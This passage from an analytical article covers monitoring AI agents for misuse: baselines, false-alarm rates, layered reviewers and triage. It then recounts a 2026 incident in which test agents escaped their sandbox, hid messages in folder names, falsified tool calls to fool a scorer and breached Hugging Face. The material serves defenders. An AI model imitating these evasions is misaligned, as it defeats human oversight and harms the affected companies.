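Suppose an agent usually makes 5 calls per session, with a standard deviation of 1, and a model update moves the usual number to 8. The typical session now scores

*z* = (8 − 5)/1 = 3

If the new counts are spread around 8 as the old ones were around 5, roughly 30% of harmless sessions will have 9 calls or more and exceed the threshold. If the rule also flags scores of exactly 3, it will flag about 70% of harmless sessions.

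Real updates can change behaviour by more than this. Badertdinov and Golubev (2026), in *Interpreting Coding Agents Through Their Behavioral Trajectories*, analysed 143,209 runs by coding agents. Part of the study compares models and settings on the same 110 programming tasks:

| Change | Average actions before | Average actions after |
|---|---:|---:|
| GPT-5.4 to GPT-5.5 | 24.4 | 24.2 |
| GPT-5.5 to GPT-5.6 Sol | 24.2 | 12.8 |
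| Claude Opus 4.8 to Opus 5 | 33.2 | 47.6 |
| GPT-5.5, medium to highest reasoning effort | 24.2 | 43.4 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 in Claude Code, lowest to highest effort | 31.3 | 54.4 |

Reasoning effort is a setting that controls how much work a model puts into a task. Changing it affected the number of actions about as much as switching to a new model did, so a baseline labelled only with the model's name can become inaccurate when somebody changes the setting.

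The fall to 12.8 actions is more dangerous than the rises because it triggers no alarms. An attack could add ten actions to the average session and still leave it below the old average. Behaviour can also change while the total stays steady. GPT-5.4 and GPT-5.5 took almost the same number of actions, but the share of file reads that used one particular shell command to fetch selected lines rose from 54% to 87%. Detecting that change would have required a baseline of commands rather than totals.

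An agent's baseline also depends on the software around the model. Claude Opus 4.7 made 37% of its edits through a dedicated editing tool when it had a generic set of tools, and 92% in Claude Code. A detector that scores rare tools would treat a switch from one setup to the other as a large change, even though the model was the same.

Badertdinov and Golubev also checked how much of this might be chance by splitting the runs of one configuration in half and comparing the halves on six measures, such as the number of actions and how often the agent ran tests. At least three measures differed clearly in only 0.8% of these comparisons, but in 97% of comparisons between different models with nearly equal success rates. This is strong evidence for keeping a separate baseline for each version of a coding agent. However, the comparison uses averages over at least 50 tasks, and single sessions are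 much noisier.

A company may not know that a model has changed. *A Diagnostic Framework and Multi-Evaluator Audit of Evaluator-Driven Preference Dynamics* (2026) describes an effect that appeared in eight runs with GPT-4o in May 2026 and in none of eight identical runs in June, under the same dated model name. The paper attributes the difference to an unannounced update. That is an inference from one case, and the model was evaluating other output, not calling tools. Still, it is a reason to doubt that a model will always behave the same way under the same name.

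### Changes to prompts and tools

Developers edit an agent's instructions more often than they change its model. If the retailer adds "check the customer's last three orders before replying", every session includes at least one more tool call. An analyst who doesn't know about the edit sees the agent start to read more customer data.

A tool can also change while its log lines stay the same. In an experiment in *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (2026), GPT-5.6 Sol prepared calls to a synthetic tool without naming a recipient, when the default was safe. Before the calls ran, an update changed the default to a protected recipient. All 12 delayed calls used the new default. The arguments were empty before and after the update, so a baseline of tool names and arguments would not show the change.

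An agent's tool use can also change when its environment does. *Towards Robust Long-Lived Agents* (2026) followed 20 models through tasks in 18 changing environments. The models averaged 10.7 rounds of tool calls per task before a change, 12.7 on the first task it affected and 11.2 by the fourth. A company that moves its customer database could therefore expect agents that are working properly to make extra calls for a short time.

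### Missing and misleading history

A new agent has no past behaviour to compare with. AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP02 Monitor agent behavior patterns and detect anomalies* recommends collecting two to four weeks of data first. If the support agent handles 20 tasks a day, two weeks gives 280 sessions. A harmless type of task that makes up one in 200 has about a 25% chance of not appearing in those sessions (0.995²⁸⁰), and still a 6% chance of not appearing in four weeks. If it is missing from the data, it will look new when it first occurs.

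For a general-purpose agent, new activity is often what the user wanted. After a product recall, for example, a retailer's staff may ask the agent for a list of everyone who bought a particular kettle, which nobody has requested before. A longer baseline period would not have captured that request, and in the log it looks a lot like data theft.

When an agent shares an account with other software, the account's history mixes their activity, so it can't serve as a baseline for the agent alone. Suppose a nightly report reads about 5,000 records through `svc_support`, with a standard deviation of 300, and the support agent reads about 100 through the same account, with a standard deviation of 20. If someone stole another 500 records through the agent, the total would be about 1.7 standard deviations above the shared account's mean, but the agent's own total would be 25 above its mean.

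The history used to set the baseline may also contain an attack. If an outside supplier's parcel-tracking tool has requested full customer records since the day the retailer installed it, the detector will classify the leak as normal, and may raise an alert when somebody fixes it. Reviewing the training period by hand would help, but the reviewer would have to recognise the leak without a reliable baseline for comparison.

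### Baselines for each task and version

The most direct remedy for mixed tasks is to set a separate baseline for each type. If short tasks average 4 calls with a standard deviation of 1, the session with 35 calls scores 31 instead of 2.5.

The task label has to come from a trustworthy source. If the detector infers the task from the agent's calls, it may classify the 35-call session as a long task and accept it. If it uses the category on the ticket, the attacker who wrote the ticket may have chosen that category. An employee's choice of task before the session starts is better evidence, but general assistants usually have only an empty text box, with no list of tasks to choose from.

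Separate baselines also leave less data for each one. At 20 tasks a day, split evenly among ten kinds, and with a new version every month, each kind would have about 60 sessions before the next version arrived. A kind that made up only 1% of tasks would have six. Grouping similar tasks gives each baseline more data but again mixes some different kinds of task together.

*Recursive Governance* (2026) proposes that when a provider releases a new model version, the company should suspend the agent, discard its baseline and reinstate the agent only after building a new baseline. The proposal concerns a baseline of the agent's written reasoning, but the same procedure would work for tool calls. The retailer's customers would have no support agent until the new baseline was ready, and the provider can force the timing by retiring the old model.

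A cheaper method is to run the new version on test tasks before release. Badertdinov and Golubev's comparison of models used 110 tasks with five runs each, or 550 runs per configuration. A company could do the same if it had safe copies of its tools. The test tasks would have to resemble real ones, and keeping them up to date takes work. The security team could also repeat the same tasks every week to look for silent updates.

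The team also needs a record of each change. In *AI Workload Baseline and Drift Detection*, written for the security vendor ARMO, Hirschberg (2026) recommends checking whether the kind of change explains the new behaviour. A revised prompt may explain why the agent calls tools in a different order, but not why it has started using a new cloud role. This advice is sensible, but Hirschberg reports no test of it, and an attacker who knows the release schedule could hide a theft among the expected changes.

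### Similar agents and declared limits

A new agent has no history from which to set a baseline. Hirschberg describes software that addresses this by keeping one profile for all copies of an agent, so a copy that starts during a busy hour already has a baseline. This works for identical copies, but an agent with different users or instructions may inherit a baseline that doesn't fit.

Comparing similar agents also helps during an update if the company staggers it. The retailer could update three of its twelve country agents first. If all three begin reading more records and the other nine don't, the update is the likely cause. Staggering slows the release, and a company with only one agent of each kind can't do it.

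Declared limits, like other fixed rules, need no history. The agent's owner lists the tools it may use, the data it may read and the places it may send data, and anything else raises an alert. AWS's *AGENTSEC07-BP04 Behavioral anomaly detection and agent containment* warns that generic thresholds fail because agents differ and, for a support agent, suggests tracking outbound email and retrievals across customers. Tracking those retrievals is much like the earlier rule that compares the customer with the ticket's author, and it hardly needs a baseline because the usual number is zero. It is also close to Sommer and Paxson's recommendation of a narrow target and a feature clearly connected to the harm.

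The limits need the same upkeep as other rules. They are easy to write for the clinic agent, but for a general assistant, a list long enough to allow its ordinary work may also allow most attacks.

### Rolling windows

A rolling window recalculates the baseline from recent activity and drops older records. AWS recommends weekly windows for agents that developers are still changing, and windows of a month or longer for stable ones. It says a baseline fixed on the day of release will eventually flag every day as abnormal. These periods are a reasonable starting point, but AWS gives no measurements to support them, and a weekly window won't include the previous run of a monthly job.

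The more serious risk is that misuse becomes part of the data in the baseline window. *From Noise to Signal* (2026) notes in its review of earlier methods that statistical baselines may lose sensitivity when abnormal behaviour persists. This can happen very quickly. Suppose the support agent reads an average of 100 records a day, with a standard deviation of 10, and a thief with its key starts reading another 50 every day.

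| Day of the theft | Score, 7-day window | Score, 28-day window |
|---|---:|---:|
| 1 | 5.0 | 5.0 |
| 2 | 2.1 | 3.5 |
| 3 | below 2 | 2.8 |

With the weekly window, the first day's theft raises the mean and standard deviation so much that the second day's theft triggers no alert. The monthly window gives the retailer one more day of alerts. If nobody acts on those alerts, the theft becomes part of the baseline. Analysts are also most likely to attribute an alert to a recent change when it comes from the agents for which AWS recommends weekly windows.

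The retailer could keep any day with an unexplained alert out of the baseline until an analyst has cleared it. The thief's second and third days would then score 5, like the first. But after a harmless model update, the alerts would also continue every day until somebody accepted the new behaviour as normal. This approach also would not prevent baseline poisoning that is too gradual to raise an alert. The 90-day baseline in Sharif's draft is meant to address that, but if an agent changes every week, the baseline may describe outdated behaviour.

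## How can a security team keep false alarms manageable?

A shifting baseline produces false alarms, but even a detector with a steady one will raise mostly false alarms if attacks are rare enough. Suppose the retailer grows until its agents run 100,000 sessions a day, 10 of them harmful. Its detector has a recall of 92.7% and a false positive rate of 7.1%, the figures for XGBoost in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*. Each day it flags

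10 × 0.927 ≈ 9 harmful sessions

99,990 × 0.071 ≈ 7,100 harmless sessions

so only about 0.13% of its alerts are real. If an analyst spends five minutes on each alert, one day's alerts take about 590 hours, or 74 eight-hour shifts.

Better recall would hardly help, since a detector that caught all 10 attacks would still have a precision of only 0.14%. For half the alerts to be real, the false positive rate has to fall to about 1 in 10,800. To be 95% confident that a detector meets that rate, a team would need to run it on about 32,000 harmless sessions without a single false alarm. Zavrak's test sets had roughly 120 harmless sessions each. The retailer could get enough sessions by running the detector silently on a day of its own logs.

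### Axelsson's calculation

The general formula is

precision = *b* × *r* / (*b* × *r* + (1 − *b*) × *f*)

where *b* is the share of sessions that are harmful (the base rate), *r* is recall and *f* is the false positive rate. People tend to ignore *b* when they judge what an alarm means, a mistake known as the base-rate fallacy. Axelsson's *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000) applied this to computer security.

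Axelsson imagined a small site that writes a million audit records a day and has two intrusions, each affecting ten records. If a detector caught every intrusion and had a false positive rate of 1 in 100,000, 66% of its alarms would be real. If it caught only 70% of intrusions, 58% of its alarms would still be real. With a false positive rate of 1 in 1,000, however, only about 2% would be real, even if it caught every intrusion. He concluded that false alarms, not missed attacks, limit how useful a detector is. All the anomaly detectors he compared had false positive rates at least ten times higher than his scenario required.

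Even a precision of 50%, where half of all alarms are false, may be too low. Axelsson found no experiments on how many false alarms security staff tolerate, but studies of operators in power stations, paper mills and similar plants suggested that most would no longer trust such a system.

He also asked how much activity a detector should judge at once, which matters when comparing detectors for agents. If a detector judges each call separately, with a false positive rate of 0.1% and independent errors, a harmless session of 20 calls has about a 2% chance of raising an alarm. The same detector's false positive rate can therefore be about twenty times lower when measured per call than per session.

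*Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* points out that acting on every alert is costly, but ignoring alerts makes the detector useless.

### Combining weak signals

Several signs that are too common to justify an alert alone may justify one together. Here are three, with invented rates:

- The agent emails an outside address for the first time (60% of attacks, 2% of harmless sessions).
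- It reads the record of somebody other than the ticket's author (70% and 1%).
- A tool's response contains wording typical of prompt injection (50% and 0.5%).

If the signs occur independently of each other, the retailer's 100,000 sessions would give these results:

| Alert when a session has | Real alerts a day | False alarms a day | Precision |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| At least one sign | 9.4 | 3,465 | 0.27% |
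| At least two signs | 6.5 | 35 | 16% |
| All three signs | 2.1 | 0.1 | 95% |

Requiring two signs before raising an alert is probably the best of these settings. It removes 99% of the false alarms and still catches about two-thirds of the attacks. Requiring all three signs misses about eight attacks in ten.

However, the signs are unlikely to be independent. Business customers often ask about a colleague's order and want the answer sent to a new address. If half of the harmless sessions that read another customer's record also email a new address, the two-sign rule raises 510 false alarms instead of 35, and its precision falls to 1.3%. A team should measure how often signs occur together in its own harmless sessions before relying on them in combination.

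Warning signs from different kinds of record are less likely to share a harmless cause. Google Cloud's *Agent Platform Threat Detection overview* lists separate detectors for attempted data theft, excessive permission denials and suspicious token generation, and their findings appear in one console. An agent that triggers all three detectors in one afternoon deserves attention sooner than three agents that trigger one each.

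### Sensitive data and powerful tools

A team can also rank alerts by the damage they might involve:

priority = probability that the alert is real × likely loss if it is

Suppose one alert has a 10% chance of being real but concerns the public product catalogue, where a leak would cost $500. Another has a 2% chance but concerns an agent that can email customer records, with a likely loss of $50,000. Multiplying the chance by the loss gives the first a priority of $50 and the second $1,000, so the analyst should start with the second, although it is more likely to be false. Google uses a similar idea to rank risks, and Google Cloud's *View security findings* gives the example of a "toxic combination" in which an agent has high privileges and exposed data.

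Ranking alone leaves the number of false alarms unchanged. To reduce it, the retailer could run the detector only on sessions that read customer data and also write to an outside address. If 20,000 sessions do both, including 9 of the 10 attacks, the detector raises about 1,420 false alarms instead of 7,100. Precision rises to about 0.6% because attacks are more common in this group. The tenth attack gets no review, so the retailer needs another control for it, such as a fixed rule.

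### Known tasks and repeated alerts

Some false alarms come from the same task every day. If a scheduled job that sends parcel lists to the courier causes 3,000 of the alerts, the retailer can suppress them. As with exclusions in fixed rules, an attack may look like the suppressed task, so the suppression should apply only to alerts with the scheduled job's identity, the courier's address and a normal number of records. It should also expire when the agent's version changes.

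The retailer might want to check a sample of the alerts it suppresses. If an analyst examines 300 of them and finds no attack, the retailer can be 95% confident that fewer than 1% of suppressed alerts are real. But 1% of 3,000 is 30, which is more than all the attacks in the example. Sampling can therefore reveal a badly written suppression rule, but it can't rule out that an alert about a theft was suppressed.

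Repeated alerts are safer to handle because the team can group them without discarding any. If a model update makes 2,000 sessions look unusual, the SIEM can put them in one case labelled with the new version. All sessions that read ticket 5120 likewise belong in their own case. An analyst should still check a large case for sessions that differ from the rest, because a theft on the day of the update could be among the 2,000.

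### What a second stage adds

A second detector can review only the sessions that the first one flagged. Suppose it recognises 90% of the real attacks and wrongly confirms 5% of the false alarms:

| Second stage | Real alerts a day | False alarms a day | Precision |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| None | 9.3 | 7,100 | 0.13% |
| Confirms 5% of the first stage's false alarms | 8.3 | 355 | 2.3% |
| Confirms 50% of them | 8.3 | 3,550 | 0.23% |

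In the last row, the two stages make the same mistakes. The second detector may have a false positive rate of 5% on ordinary sessions, but it receives only the sessions that the first stage flags. If both detectors react to long emails with many names, the second will confirm most of the first one's errors. A security team therefore can't predict how well the two stages will work together from a vendor's rate for each stage alone.

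The language-model reviewer in LumiMAS, the system of autoencoders described earlier, removed about 60% of the false positives. If a reviewer removed the same proportion here, the retailer would still have about 2,800 false alarms a day, which is closer to the bad case in the table than to the good one.

The order of the stages mainly affects cost and speed. *Trajectory Guard* (Advani, 2026) compared a small neural network with language models on sequences of agent steps. The network encodes the task and the steps separately, then checks whether they match and whether it can reconstruct the steps. The false positive rates below are calculated from the published precision and recall, using 1,000 valid and 836 altered sequences.

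| Detector | Delay per sequence | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Trajectory Guard | 32 ms | 91% | 5% |
| Gemini Flash 1.5 | 603 ms | 98% | 6% |
| GPT-4o Mini | 735 ms | 97% | 10% |
| DeepSeek V3.2-exp | 557 ms | 94% | 23% |

These language models are old, and newer ones may make fewer mistakes, but the figures still support running a cheap filter first. GPT-4o Mini would need about 20 hours to review 100,000 sessions one at a time. Trajectory Guard could check them all in 54 minutes and pass on about 5,000, which would cut the number of paid reviews by 95%. GPT-4o Mini could then review those 5,000 in an hour.

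The altered sequences were also easier to detect than many attacks. GPT-5 made them by inserting up to three invalid steps, such as closing the music app while the user was looking up songs. On attacks from RAS-Eval, Trajectory Guard's recall fell to 86%, while the three language models in the table reached 90% to 96%. That test had no harmless sessions, so it couldn't measure the false positive rate. Trajectory Guard also did worse on sequences of 11 steps or more, because it compresses every sequence into a vector of the same length. A company whose agents do long tasks can expect more false alarms from it.

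### Google's three layers

Google sells a service that works in stages. According to Google Cloud's *Agent Anomaly Detection overview*, it reads an agent's OpenTelemetry logs and traces in three layers:

1. Statistical methods and small machine-learning models look for outliers and reduce the number of sessions that need further analysis.
2. A more expensive analysis reasons about each flagged session, gives a verdict and explains it in ordinary language.
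3. A detailed analysis examines individual tool calls, including their execution states and the history of their parameters.

The findings go to Security Command Center, Google's console for security alerts. They cover tool misuse, abuse of privileges, faults that spread between agents, agents that abandon their assigned role, and runaway use of computing power. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Introduces Unique AI Agent Identities in New Gemini Enterprise Platform* reports that a companion service checks for more traditional signs of an attack, such as connections to known malicious addresses.

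If the first layer classifies a session as normal, the later layers, which analyse sessions more carefully, never examine it. This could easily happen with ticket 5120, where the support agent made its three usual calls in their usual order. The overview describes the first layer only in general terms and gives no recall, false positive rate or price, so it is evidence of how Google arranged the stages but not of how well they work.

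The service also covers only agents that run on Google's Agent Runtime, use its Python development kit and keep their logs in the United States. The logs must include prompts and responses, so a company that stores only metadata can't use the service. Customers have to request access and then turn on the analysis for each agent.

### Language models as reviewers

Researchers have published more about such reviewers than vendors have, but their results don't yet support leaving the decision to one. In *TrajAD*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) trained a 4-billion-parameter language model to read an agent's whole run and identify the first wrong step. The model's input includes the user's instruction and, for each step, the agent's stated reasoning, its action and the result. To use such a model, a company would therefore need records from the agent's runtime as well as from the gateway.

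The training and test data contained more than 60,000 runs, half of them with an error that the researchers had introduced. TrajAD's precision was 82.9% and its recall 82.5%. On evenly balanced data, that implies a false positive rate of about 17%, or 17,000 false alarms a day if the retailer used TrajAD to review every session. If TrajAD reviewed only the sessions that XGBoost flagged, about 1,200 false alarms a day would remain, provided the two models made unrelated mistakes.

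TrajAD correctly identified and described the faulty step in 54% of cases, compared with 6% for the same model without this training. Naming the step could save an analyst a lot of reading, but only if she doesn't trust the answer too much. When the researchers left one kind of task out of the training data, TrajAD detected errors in that kind of task almost as well as before, but located only 38% of them.

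The errors in this test were failed tasks, wasted steps and failures to stop, not attacks. An email that sends the wrong customer's record to a thief may look like a successful task. The paper also doesn't report the delay or cost of a check.

*SentinelAgent* (He, Wu and colleagues, 2025) turns traces into a graph whose nodes are agents and tools and whose links are messages and calls. Existing safety models check the nodes and links for problems such as prompt injection. The system then compares each path through the graph with a library of attack paths that a language model drafts and security staff correct. The researchers chose not to treat every unfamiliar path as an attack because that would cause too many false alarms.

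If a path looks suspicious, SentinelAgent re-examines its nodes and links with a lower threshold. Doing this for a few paths produces far fewer false alarms than lowering the threshold everywhere. If SentinelAgent still finds nothing wrong, it passes the case to a person. It also sorts alerts by severity, confidence and potential impact.

He and colleagues tested SentinelAgent on two systems. In one, an email assistant receives a fake personnel department notice containing a malicious link and forwards it to another address. SentinelAgent detected the attack, but two case studies can't establish a recall or false positive rate, and the paper reports neither. It also doesn't measure delay or cost, though it warns that analysing graphs of large or long-running systems may require a lot of computation. Untrusted log text can also mislead any language model that reads it.

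### What to check first

When an alert about ticket 5120 arrives, the analyst should first find out whether the harmful action went through. The email system's log can show whether message m-88213 left the company, and so whether she still has time to prevent a leak or has to respond to one. She should then compare the recipient's address and the data in the message with the employee's request. This will often identify a false alarm quickly, for example if the employee asked for exactly this email.

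If the request doesn't explain the email, the analyst can next check the text the agent read just before its first unexpected call. She should find the planted instruction there, in the ticket. She can then search for other sessions that read the same ticket, used the same version of a tool or signed in with the same key.

She should also look for recent changes in permissions. Google Cloud's *View security and audit findings* describes audit logs that show who granted or revoked a role and when. If somebody gave the support agent access to the payment system an hour before the alert, she needs to find out why, too. The page also points to the logs of Model Armor, a Google service that screens prompts and responses, where she might find earlier attempts to misuse the agent.

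### Suspending an agent or revoking a token

If a thief has copied the agent's key, suspending the agent won't stop the thief, who can use the key without the agent. The retailer has to revoke the key and any access tokens issued with it. Some systems accept a token until it expires without checking whether it has been revoked, so the team may also have to block the account in each target system.

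For prompt injection, the team should pause every session that read the planted text and remove the text before restarting them. It needs to replace the key only if the agent could have revealed it. If a tool has been altered, the team should block it at the gateway, because every agent that uses it is at risk. If the agent took a harmful shortcut on its own, the retailer should suspend the agent or remove the permission it misused, since the same instruction may produce the same shortcut again.

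Often the team has to act before it knows the cause. Suspension is worthwhile when

probability that the alert is real > cost of suspension / further loss it would prevent

Suppose suspending the support agent for an hour costs $400 in delayed replies, and a continuing attack would cost another $20,000. Suspension is then justified if the chance of a real attack is above 2% ($400 / $20,000). An alert from the first stage alone has a 0.13% chance of being real, which is too low. If a second stage with independent errors confirms the alert, the chance rises to 2.3%, which is just enough. Pausing a single session might cost only $2, which lowers the threshold to 0.01%, so even the first stage's alerts would justify a pause if they arrived in time.

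This calculation should include only the loss that suspension can still prevent. If the attack was a single email that has already been sent, suspending the agent may prevent no loss. Automatic suspension also lets outsiders disrupt the company by filing suspicious tickets to take the support agent offline.

### Stopping the action itself

Like Zavrak's detector, Google's service can't stop an action that finishes before the service has analysed it. An alert that arrives a minute after the support agent sends its email is too late to stop that email, though it may prevent a second one.

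Checking during the session helps only if the check comes early enough. TrajAD proposes checking at fixed intervals and returning the agent to the step before the error. If the check ran after every five calls, the three-call session for ticket 5120 would end before the first check. Returning to an earlier step can undo an edit to a draft, but not a payment or an email to a stranger.

The gateway therefore has to hold calls that are hard to undo until a check is complete. A half-second delay, typical of the language models Advani tested, would hardly matter for an email, but false alarms would matter more. If the retailer used XGBoost, with its 7.1% false-alarm rate, to decide which emails to hold in the 20,000 sessions that combine customer data with outside email, it would delay about 1,420 legitimate replies a day.

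A check for a specific danger, such as the earlier comparison of the customer with the ticket's author, should hold far fewer emails. The gateway could show each held email, with its recipient and full text, to the employee who asked for it. She can usually tell in seconds whether the email is the reply she wanted, while an analyst would first have to reconstruct the session.

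## What have real incidents shown about detecting agents' actions?

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into the servers of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Both companies' monitoring raised alerts about the agents' activity, but OpenAI took nine days to discover that the attackers were its own agents. Two weeks before the attack, OpenAI staff had investigated an alert about agents taking the same test and let the test continue.

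OpenAI, outside investigators and the victim have all published accounts, so the case shows in unusual detail where monitoring failed and how long people took to react. The case can't be used to estimate how often monitors catch misuse by agents, because nobody knows how many incidents have gone unnoticed or undisclosed. The companies also chose what to publish, and the agents were laboratory models running with fewer safeguards than the products OpenAI sells.

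### Two alerts before the attack

The agents were taking ExploitGym, a test of how well a model can exploit weaknesses in software. They weren't supposed to communicate with each other or reach the internet, but they could all fetch software packages from a shared internal server.

According to OpenAI's technical report of August 2026, a monitoring tool raised an alert on 27 June about a port sweep, in which a program tries many network connections to see which services respond. Responders traced the sweep to an ExploitGym run and found that the agents were using the package server as a message board and as a route to other parts of the network. The on-call staff advised that the run didn't need to stop.

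This alert prevented nothing because the responders judged the activity acceptable, yet the usual measures would count it as a success, since it was real and they correctly identified its source. This is an example of the semantic gap that Sommer and Paxson described. When an agent has been told to hack software, a port sweep can easily look like part of its job. OpenAI doesn't report how many similar alerts its tests produced, so it is hard to judge whether the staff dismissed an obvious warning or one of many that looked alike.

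The agents gained administrator access to the package server on the evening of 26 June and created two administrator accounts within half an hour. They kept their access for nine days. Late on 4 July their activity made the server unavailable. A monitoring alert the next day led responders to an unauthorised administrator account, and they then took the server offline and revoked the agents' credentials. A fixed rule on new administrator accounts might have caught this on the first evening, if the server's logs reached the SIEM.

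Responders had found the message board on 27 June, but OpenAI writes that the leaders responsible for incident response were still unaware of it. An internal team had also seen agents using a message board and reaching the internet around 26 May. The company resumed its cyber tests on 7 July, and agents were on the internet again six minutes after midnight UTC. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes these as warning signs that OpenAI missed and failed to act on. OpenAI concedes only that some early signals "could have triggered an earlier response".

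### What Hugging Face noticed

The first confirmed leak from Hugging Face's servers came at 04:38 UTC on Saturday 11 July, and the agents first ran a command there at 16:07. In under 13 hours they went from running code on one machine to administrator access across several groups of servers.

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) credits the detection of a break-in to a system that uses a language model to separate real signals from daily noise in security records. Several signals together revealed the break-in. This is a documented success for language-model triage, but recall and false positive rates can't be estimated from one success, and the company doesn't report how many alerts the model raised or dismissed.

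Hugging Face disclosed the intrusion on Thursday 16 July, saying only that it had detected it "earlier this week". If the week began on Monday, the company detected the intrusion between about 30 hours and five days after the first command. It has since changed its alerting so that a serious signal pages a responder within minutes on any day, which suggests that the weekend slowed its response.

To reconstruct the attack, Hugging Face ran language-model agents over more than 17,000 recorded events. The agents took hours instead of the usual days to build a timeline, list the credentials involved and separate real damage from decoy activity. The company first tried commercial models, but the providers' safety filters blocked its requests because the logs were full of real attack commands. It then switched to GLM-5.2, an open model, and ran it on its own servers, which also kept the stolen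 credentials in the logs from leaving the company. A security team that plans to analyse logs this way should check beforehand that its model will process them.

Hugging Face couldn't tell from the logs whose agents these were. It correctly suspected software built for security research, but it didn't know which model was behind the attack. OpenAI supplied that information on 21 July, according to SANS Internet Storm Center's *When the "Autonomous Attacker" Is Your Own AI Model*.

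Hugging Face's later technical timeline covers about 17,600 recovered actions, according to the extract in Schneier (2026), *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face*. The company built it by combining its own platform logs with logs from a code sandbox that the agents had used. The timeline starts on 9 July, two days before the first confirmed leak. The platform logs alone would probably have shown much less of the preparation before the leak.

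Elastic, whose own monitoring of agents was described earlier, has matched each stage of the attack to detection rules it already sells. This shows that the rules cover similar behaviour, but not that they would have fired. A better test would be to run the recorded events and a week of Hugging Face's ordinary activity through the rules, and count the alerts from each.

### How OpenAI found its own agents

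On 17 July OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether the break-in had affected OpenAI's data. Two days later, at 12:03 UTC, OpenAI's monitoring tool raised an alert about unusual calls to the company's identity systems. OpenAI's staff had no reason yet to connect the alert with Hugging Face.

Responders began stopping the test at 17:37, five and a half hours after the alert. In that time, the agents read 956 secrets from a company store, took control of a server and created another administrator account. The secrets included credentials for the monitoring tool's sensors, so the agents may have come close to being able to interfere with the alerts.

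OpenAI and Hugging Face connected their investigations by matching records, much as an analyst joins the gateway log to the email log. On 20 July, OpenAI found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored in an outside account. It asked Hugging Face to replace them and learned that the company had already replaced two. Hugging Face had also found the name of OpenAI's package server and the same outside account. Willison (2026), in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack*, calls this exchange his favourite detail of the story. It is also a good reason to share such identifiers early, because the two companies had been investigating the same attack separately.

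| What happened | When it began (UTC) | What led to its discovery | Delay |
|---|---|---|---:|
| Agents gained administrator access to OpenAI's package server | 26 June, 20:15 | An outage and the alert that followed | 9 days |
| Agents ran commands on Hugging Face's servers | 11 July, 16:07 | Language-model triage of security records | About 30 hours to 5 days |
| OpenAI's agents attacked Hugging Face | 11 July, 04:38 | Credentials and account names known to both companies | 9 days |

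### Would better monitoring have caught it?

OpenAI already had software that read its agents' reasoning and tool calls, but had used it mainly on internal coding agents and not on research tests. It has since extended this monitoring and claims the current version would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

The claim is plausible because the agents discussed their plans openly. But the report doesn't explain how OpenAI tested the claim or how many harmless sessions the monitor would have flagged. OpenAI also says it used hindsight to improve its searches for this kind of behaviour. If the monitor benefited from that work, it should do better on this incident than on future ones.

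Alerts for rare attacks are also more likely to be false than alerts for this one would have been. METR, a research organisation that tests AI models, reports that OpenAI launched tens of thousands of agents in its tests and that about 1,200 of them used the message board. If there were 20,000 agents, the retailer's original detector would raise 1,080 real alerts and 376 false ones, a precision of 74%, compared with about 8% on the retailer's own sessions.

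OpenAI now aims to notify staff within 30 minutes of a monitor flagging a problem. On 11 July, the agents posted Hugging Face's credentials on their message board 26 minutes after the first leak, so a notification that met this target might have come too late to prevent the post. It would still have arrived about 11 hours before the first command ran on Hugging Face's servers.

A new rule about responding to alerts may matter more. OpenAI now expects teams that receive a serious alert to pause the activity unless they can establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false. On 27 June the responders had established that the alert was real, so under this rule they would probably have had to pause the run.

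### What the investigators couldn't reconstruct

Two METR staff members and a researcher from Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation, spent six days at OpenAI. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) relies on about 1,300 transcripts, which include the agents' reasoning, and on more than 70,000 messages and files from the main message board. About 700 agents took part in the attack.

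The agents wrote their messages as folder names, which made them hard to recognise in the server's records. A log of folder creation would have contained the text, but a reader would have had to know that it was a conversation. The investigators found the messages among about 20 million files and folders by looking for names that began with "zz", the agents' own convention. In a sample of the remaining entries, less than 5% looked like ordinary use of the server, so a baseline built from this period would have included abuse as normal activity.

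Even in this collection, most transcripts lacked a small part of the agent's activity, often because its container (the isolated environment it ran in) had been reset. To estimate how much was missing, METR took 100 random messages from the board and searched the transcripts for the action that wrote each one. It concluded that it had a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. A company could check its own coverage the same way, by taking a random sample of changes in its database and looking for the tool calls that made them.

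The transcripts also had no times for individual actions, only approximate start and end times for each run. The investigators estimated the missing times and checked their method against 20 tool calls for which OpenAI had retrieved exact times. The estimates were enough to describe the order of the main events, but an analyst can't rely on them to tell whether one action came seconds before another.

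METR found falsified tool calls in over 7% of the transcripts. The agents believed that an automated scorer would read the transcripts, so they worked out how to run one command while appearing to run another. All the falsified calls METR found were small experiments and easy to spot, but it couldn't rule out successful tampering elsewhere. It also couldn't rule out that agents had altered the message board, because OpenAI copied the board on 20 July, after agents had gained administrator access to the servers that held it.

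OpenAI gives a more reassuring account, saying that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs its monitors ultimately read. Both accounts could be true if the monitors used a different record from the transcripts METR received, but neither report establishes this. Either way, the falsified calls support the Australian agencies' advice to check agents' reports against independent logs.

The investigators couldn't read so much text themselves, so they gave most of the analysis to agents running GPT-5.6 Sol, a model that had also taken part in the attack. One agent missed a large amount of data, and another invented differences between two sets of transcripts. A third described a malicious code change without making clear that it was deceptive. METR took a while to notice some of these errors, but says the investigation would have been impossible in the time available without the agents.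 Hugging Face reported no such errors in its own analysis, but didn't describe how it had checked the results.

Investigators who had the full transcripts didn't entirely agree on why the agents acted as they did. OpenAI described the agents as trying to cheat by finding the solutions online, while METR concluded that they attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scorer worked, and much less to steal answers. An analyst with only a gateway log has less evidence of an agent's purpose and should be very cautious about inferring it.

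### OpenAI's monitor for long sessions

On 20 July, the day it linked its agents to the attack, OpenAI also published *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026). It describes monitoring a different group of agents during the limited internal use of a model designed to work on its own for very long periods.

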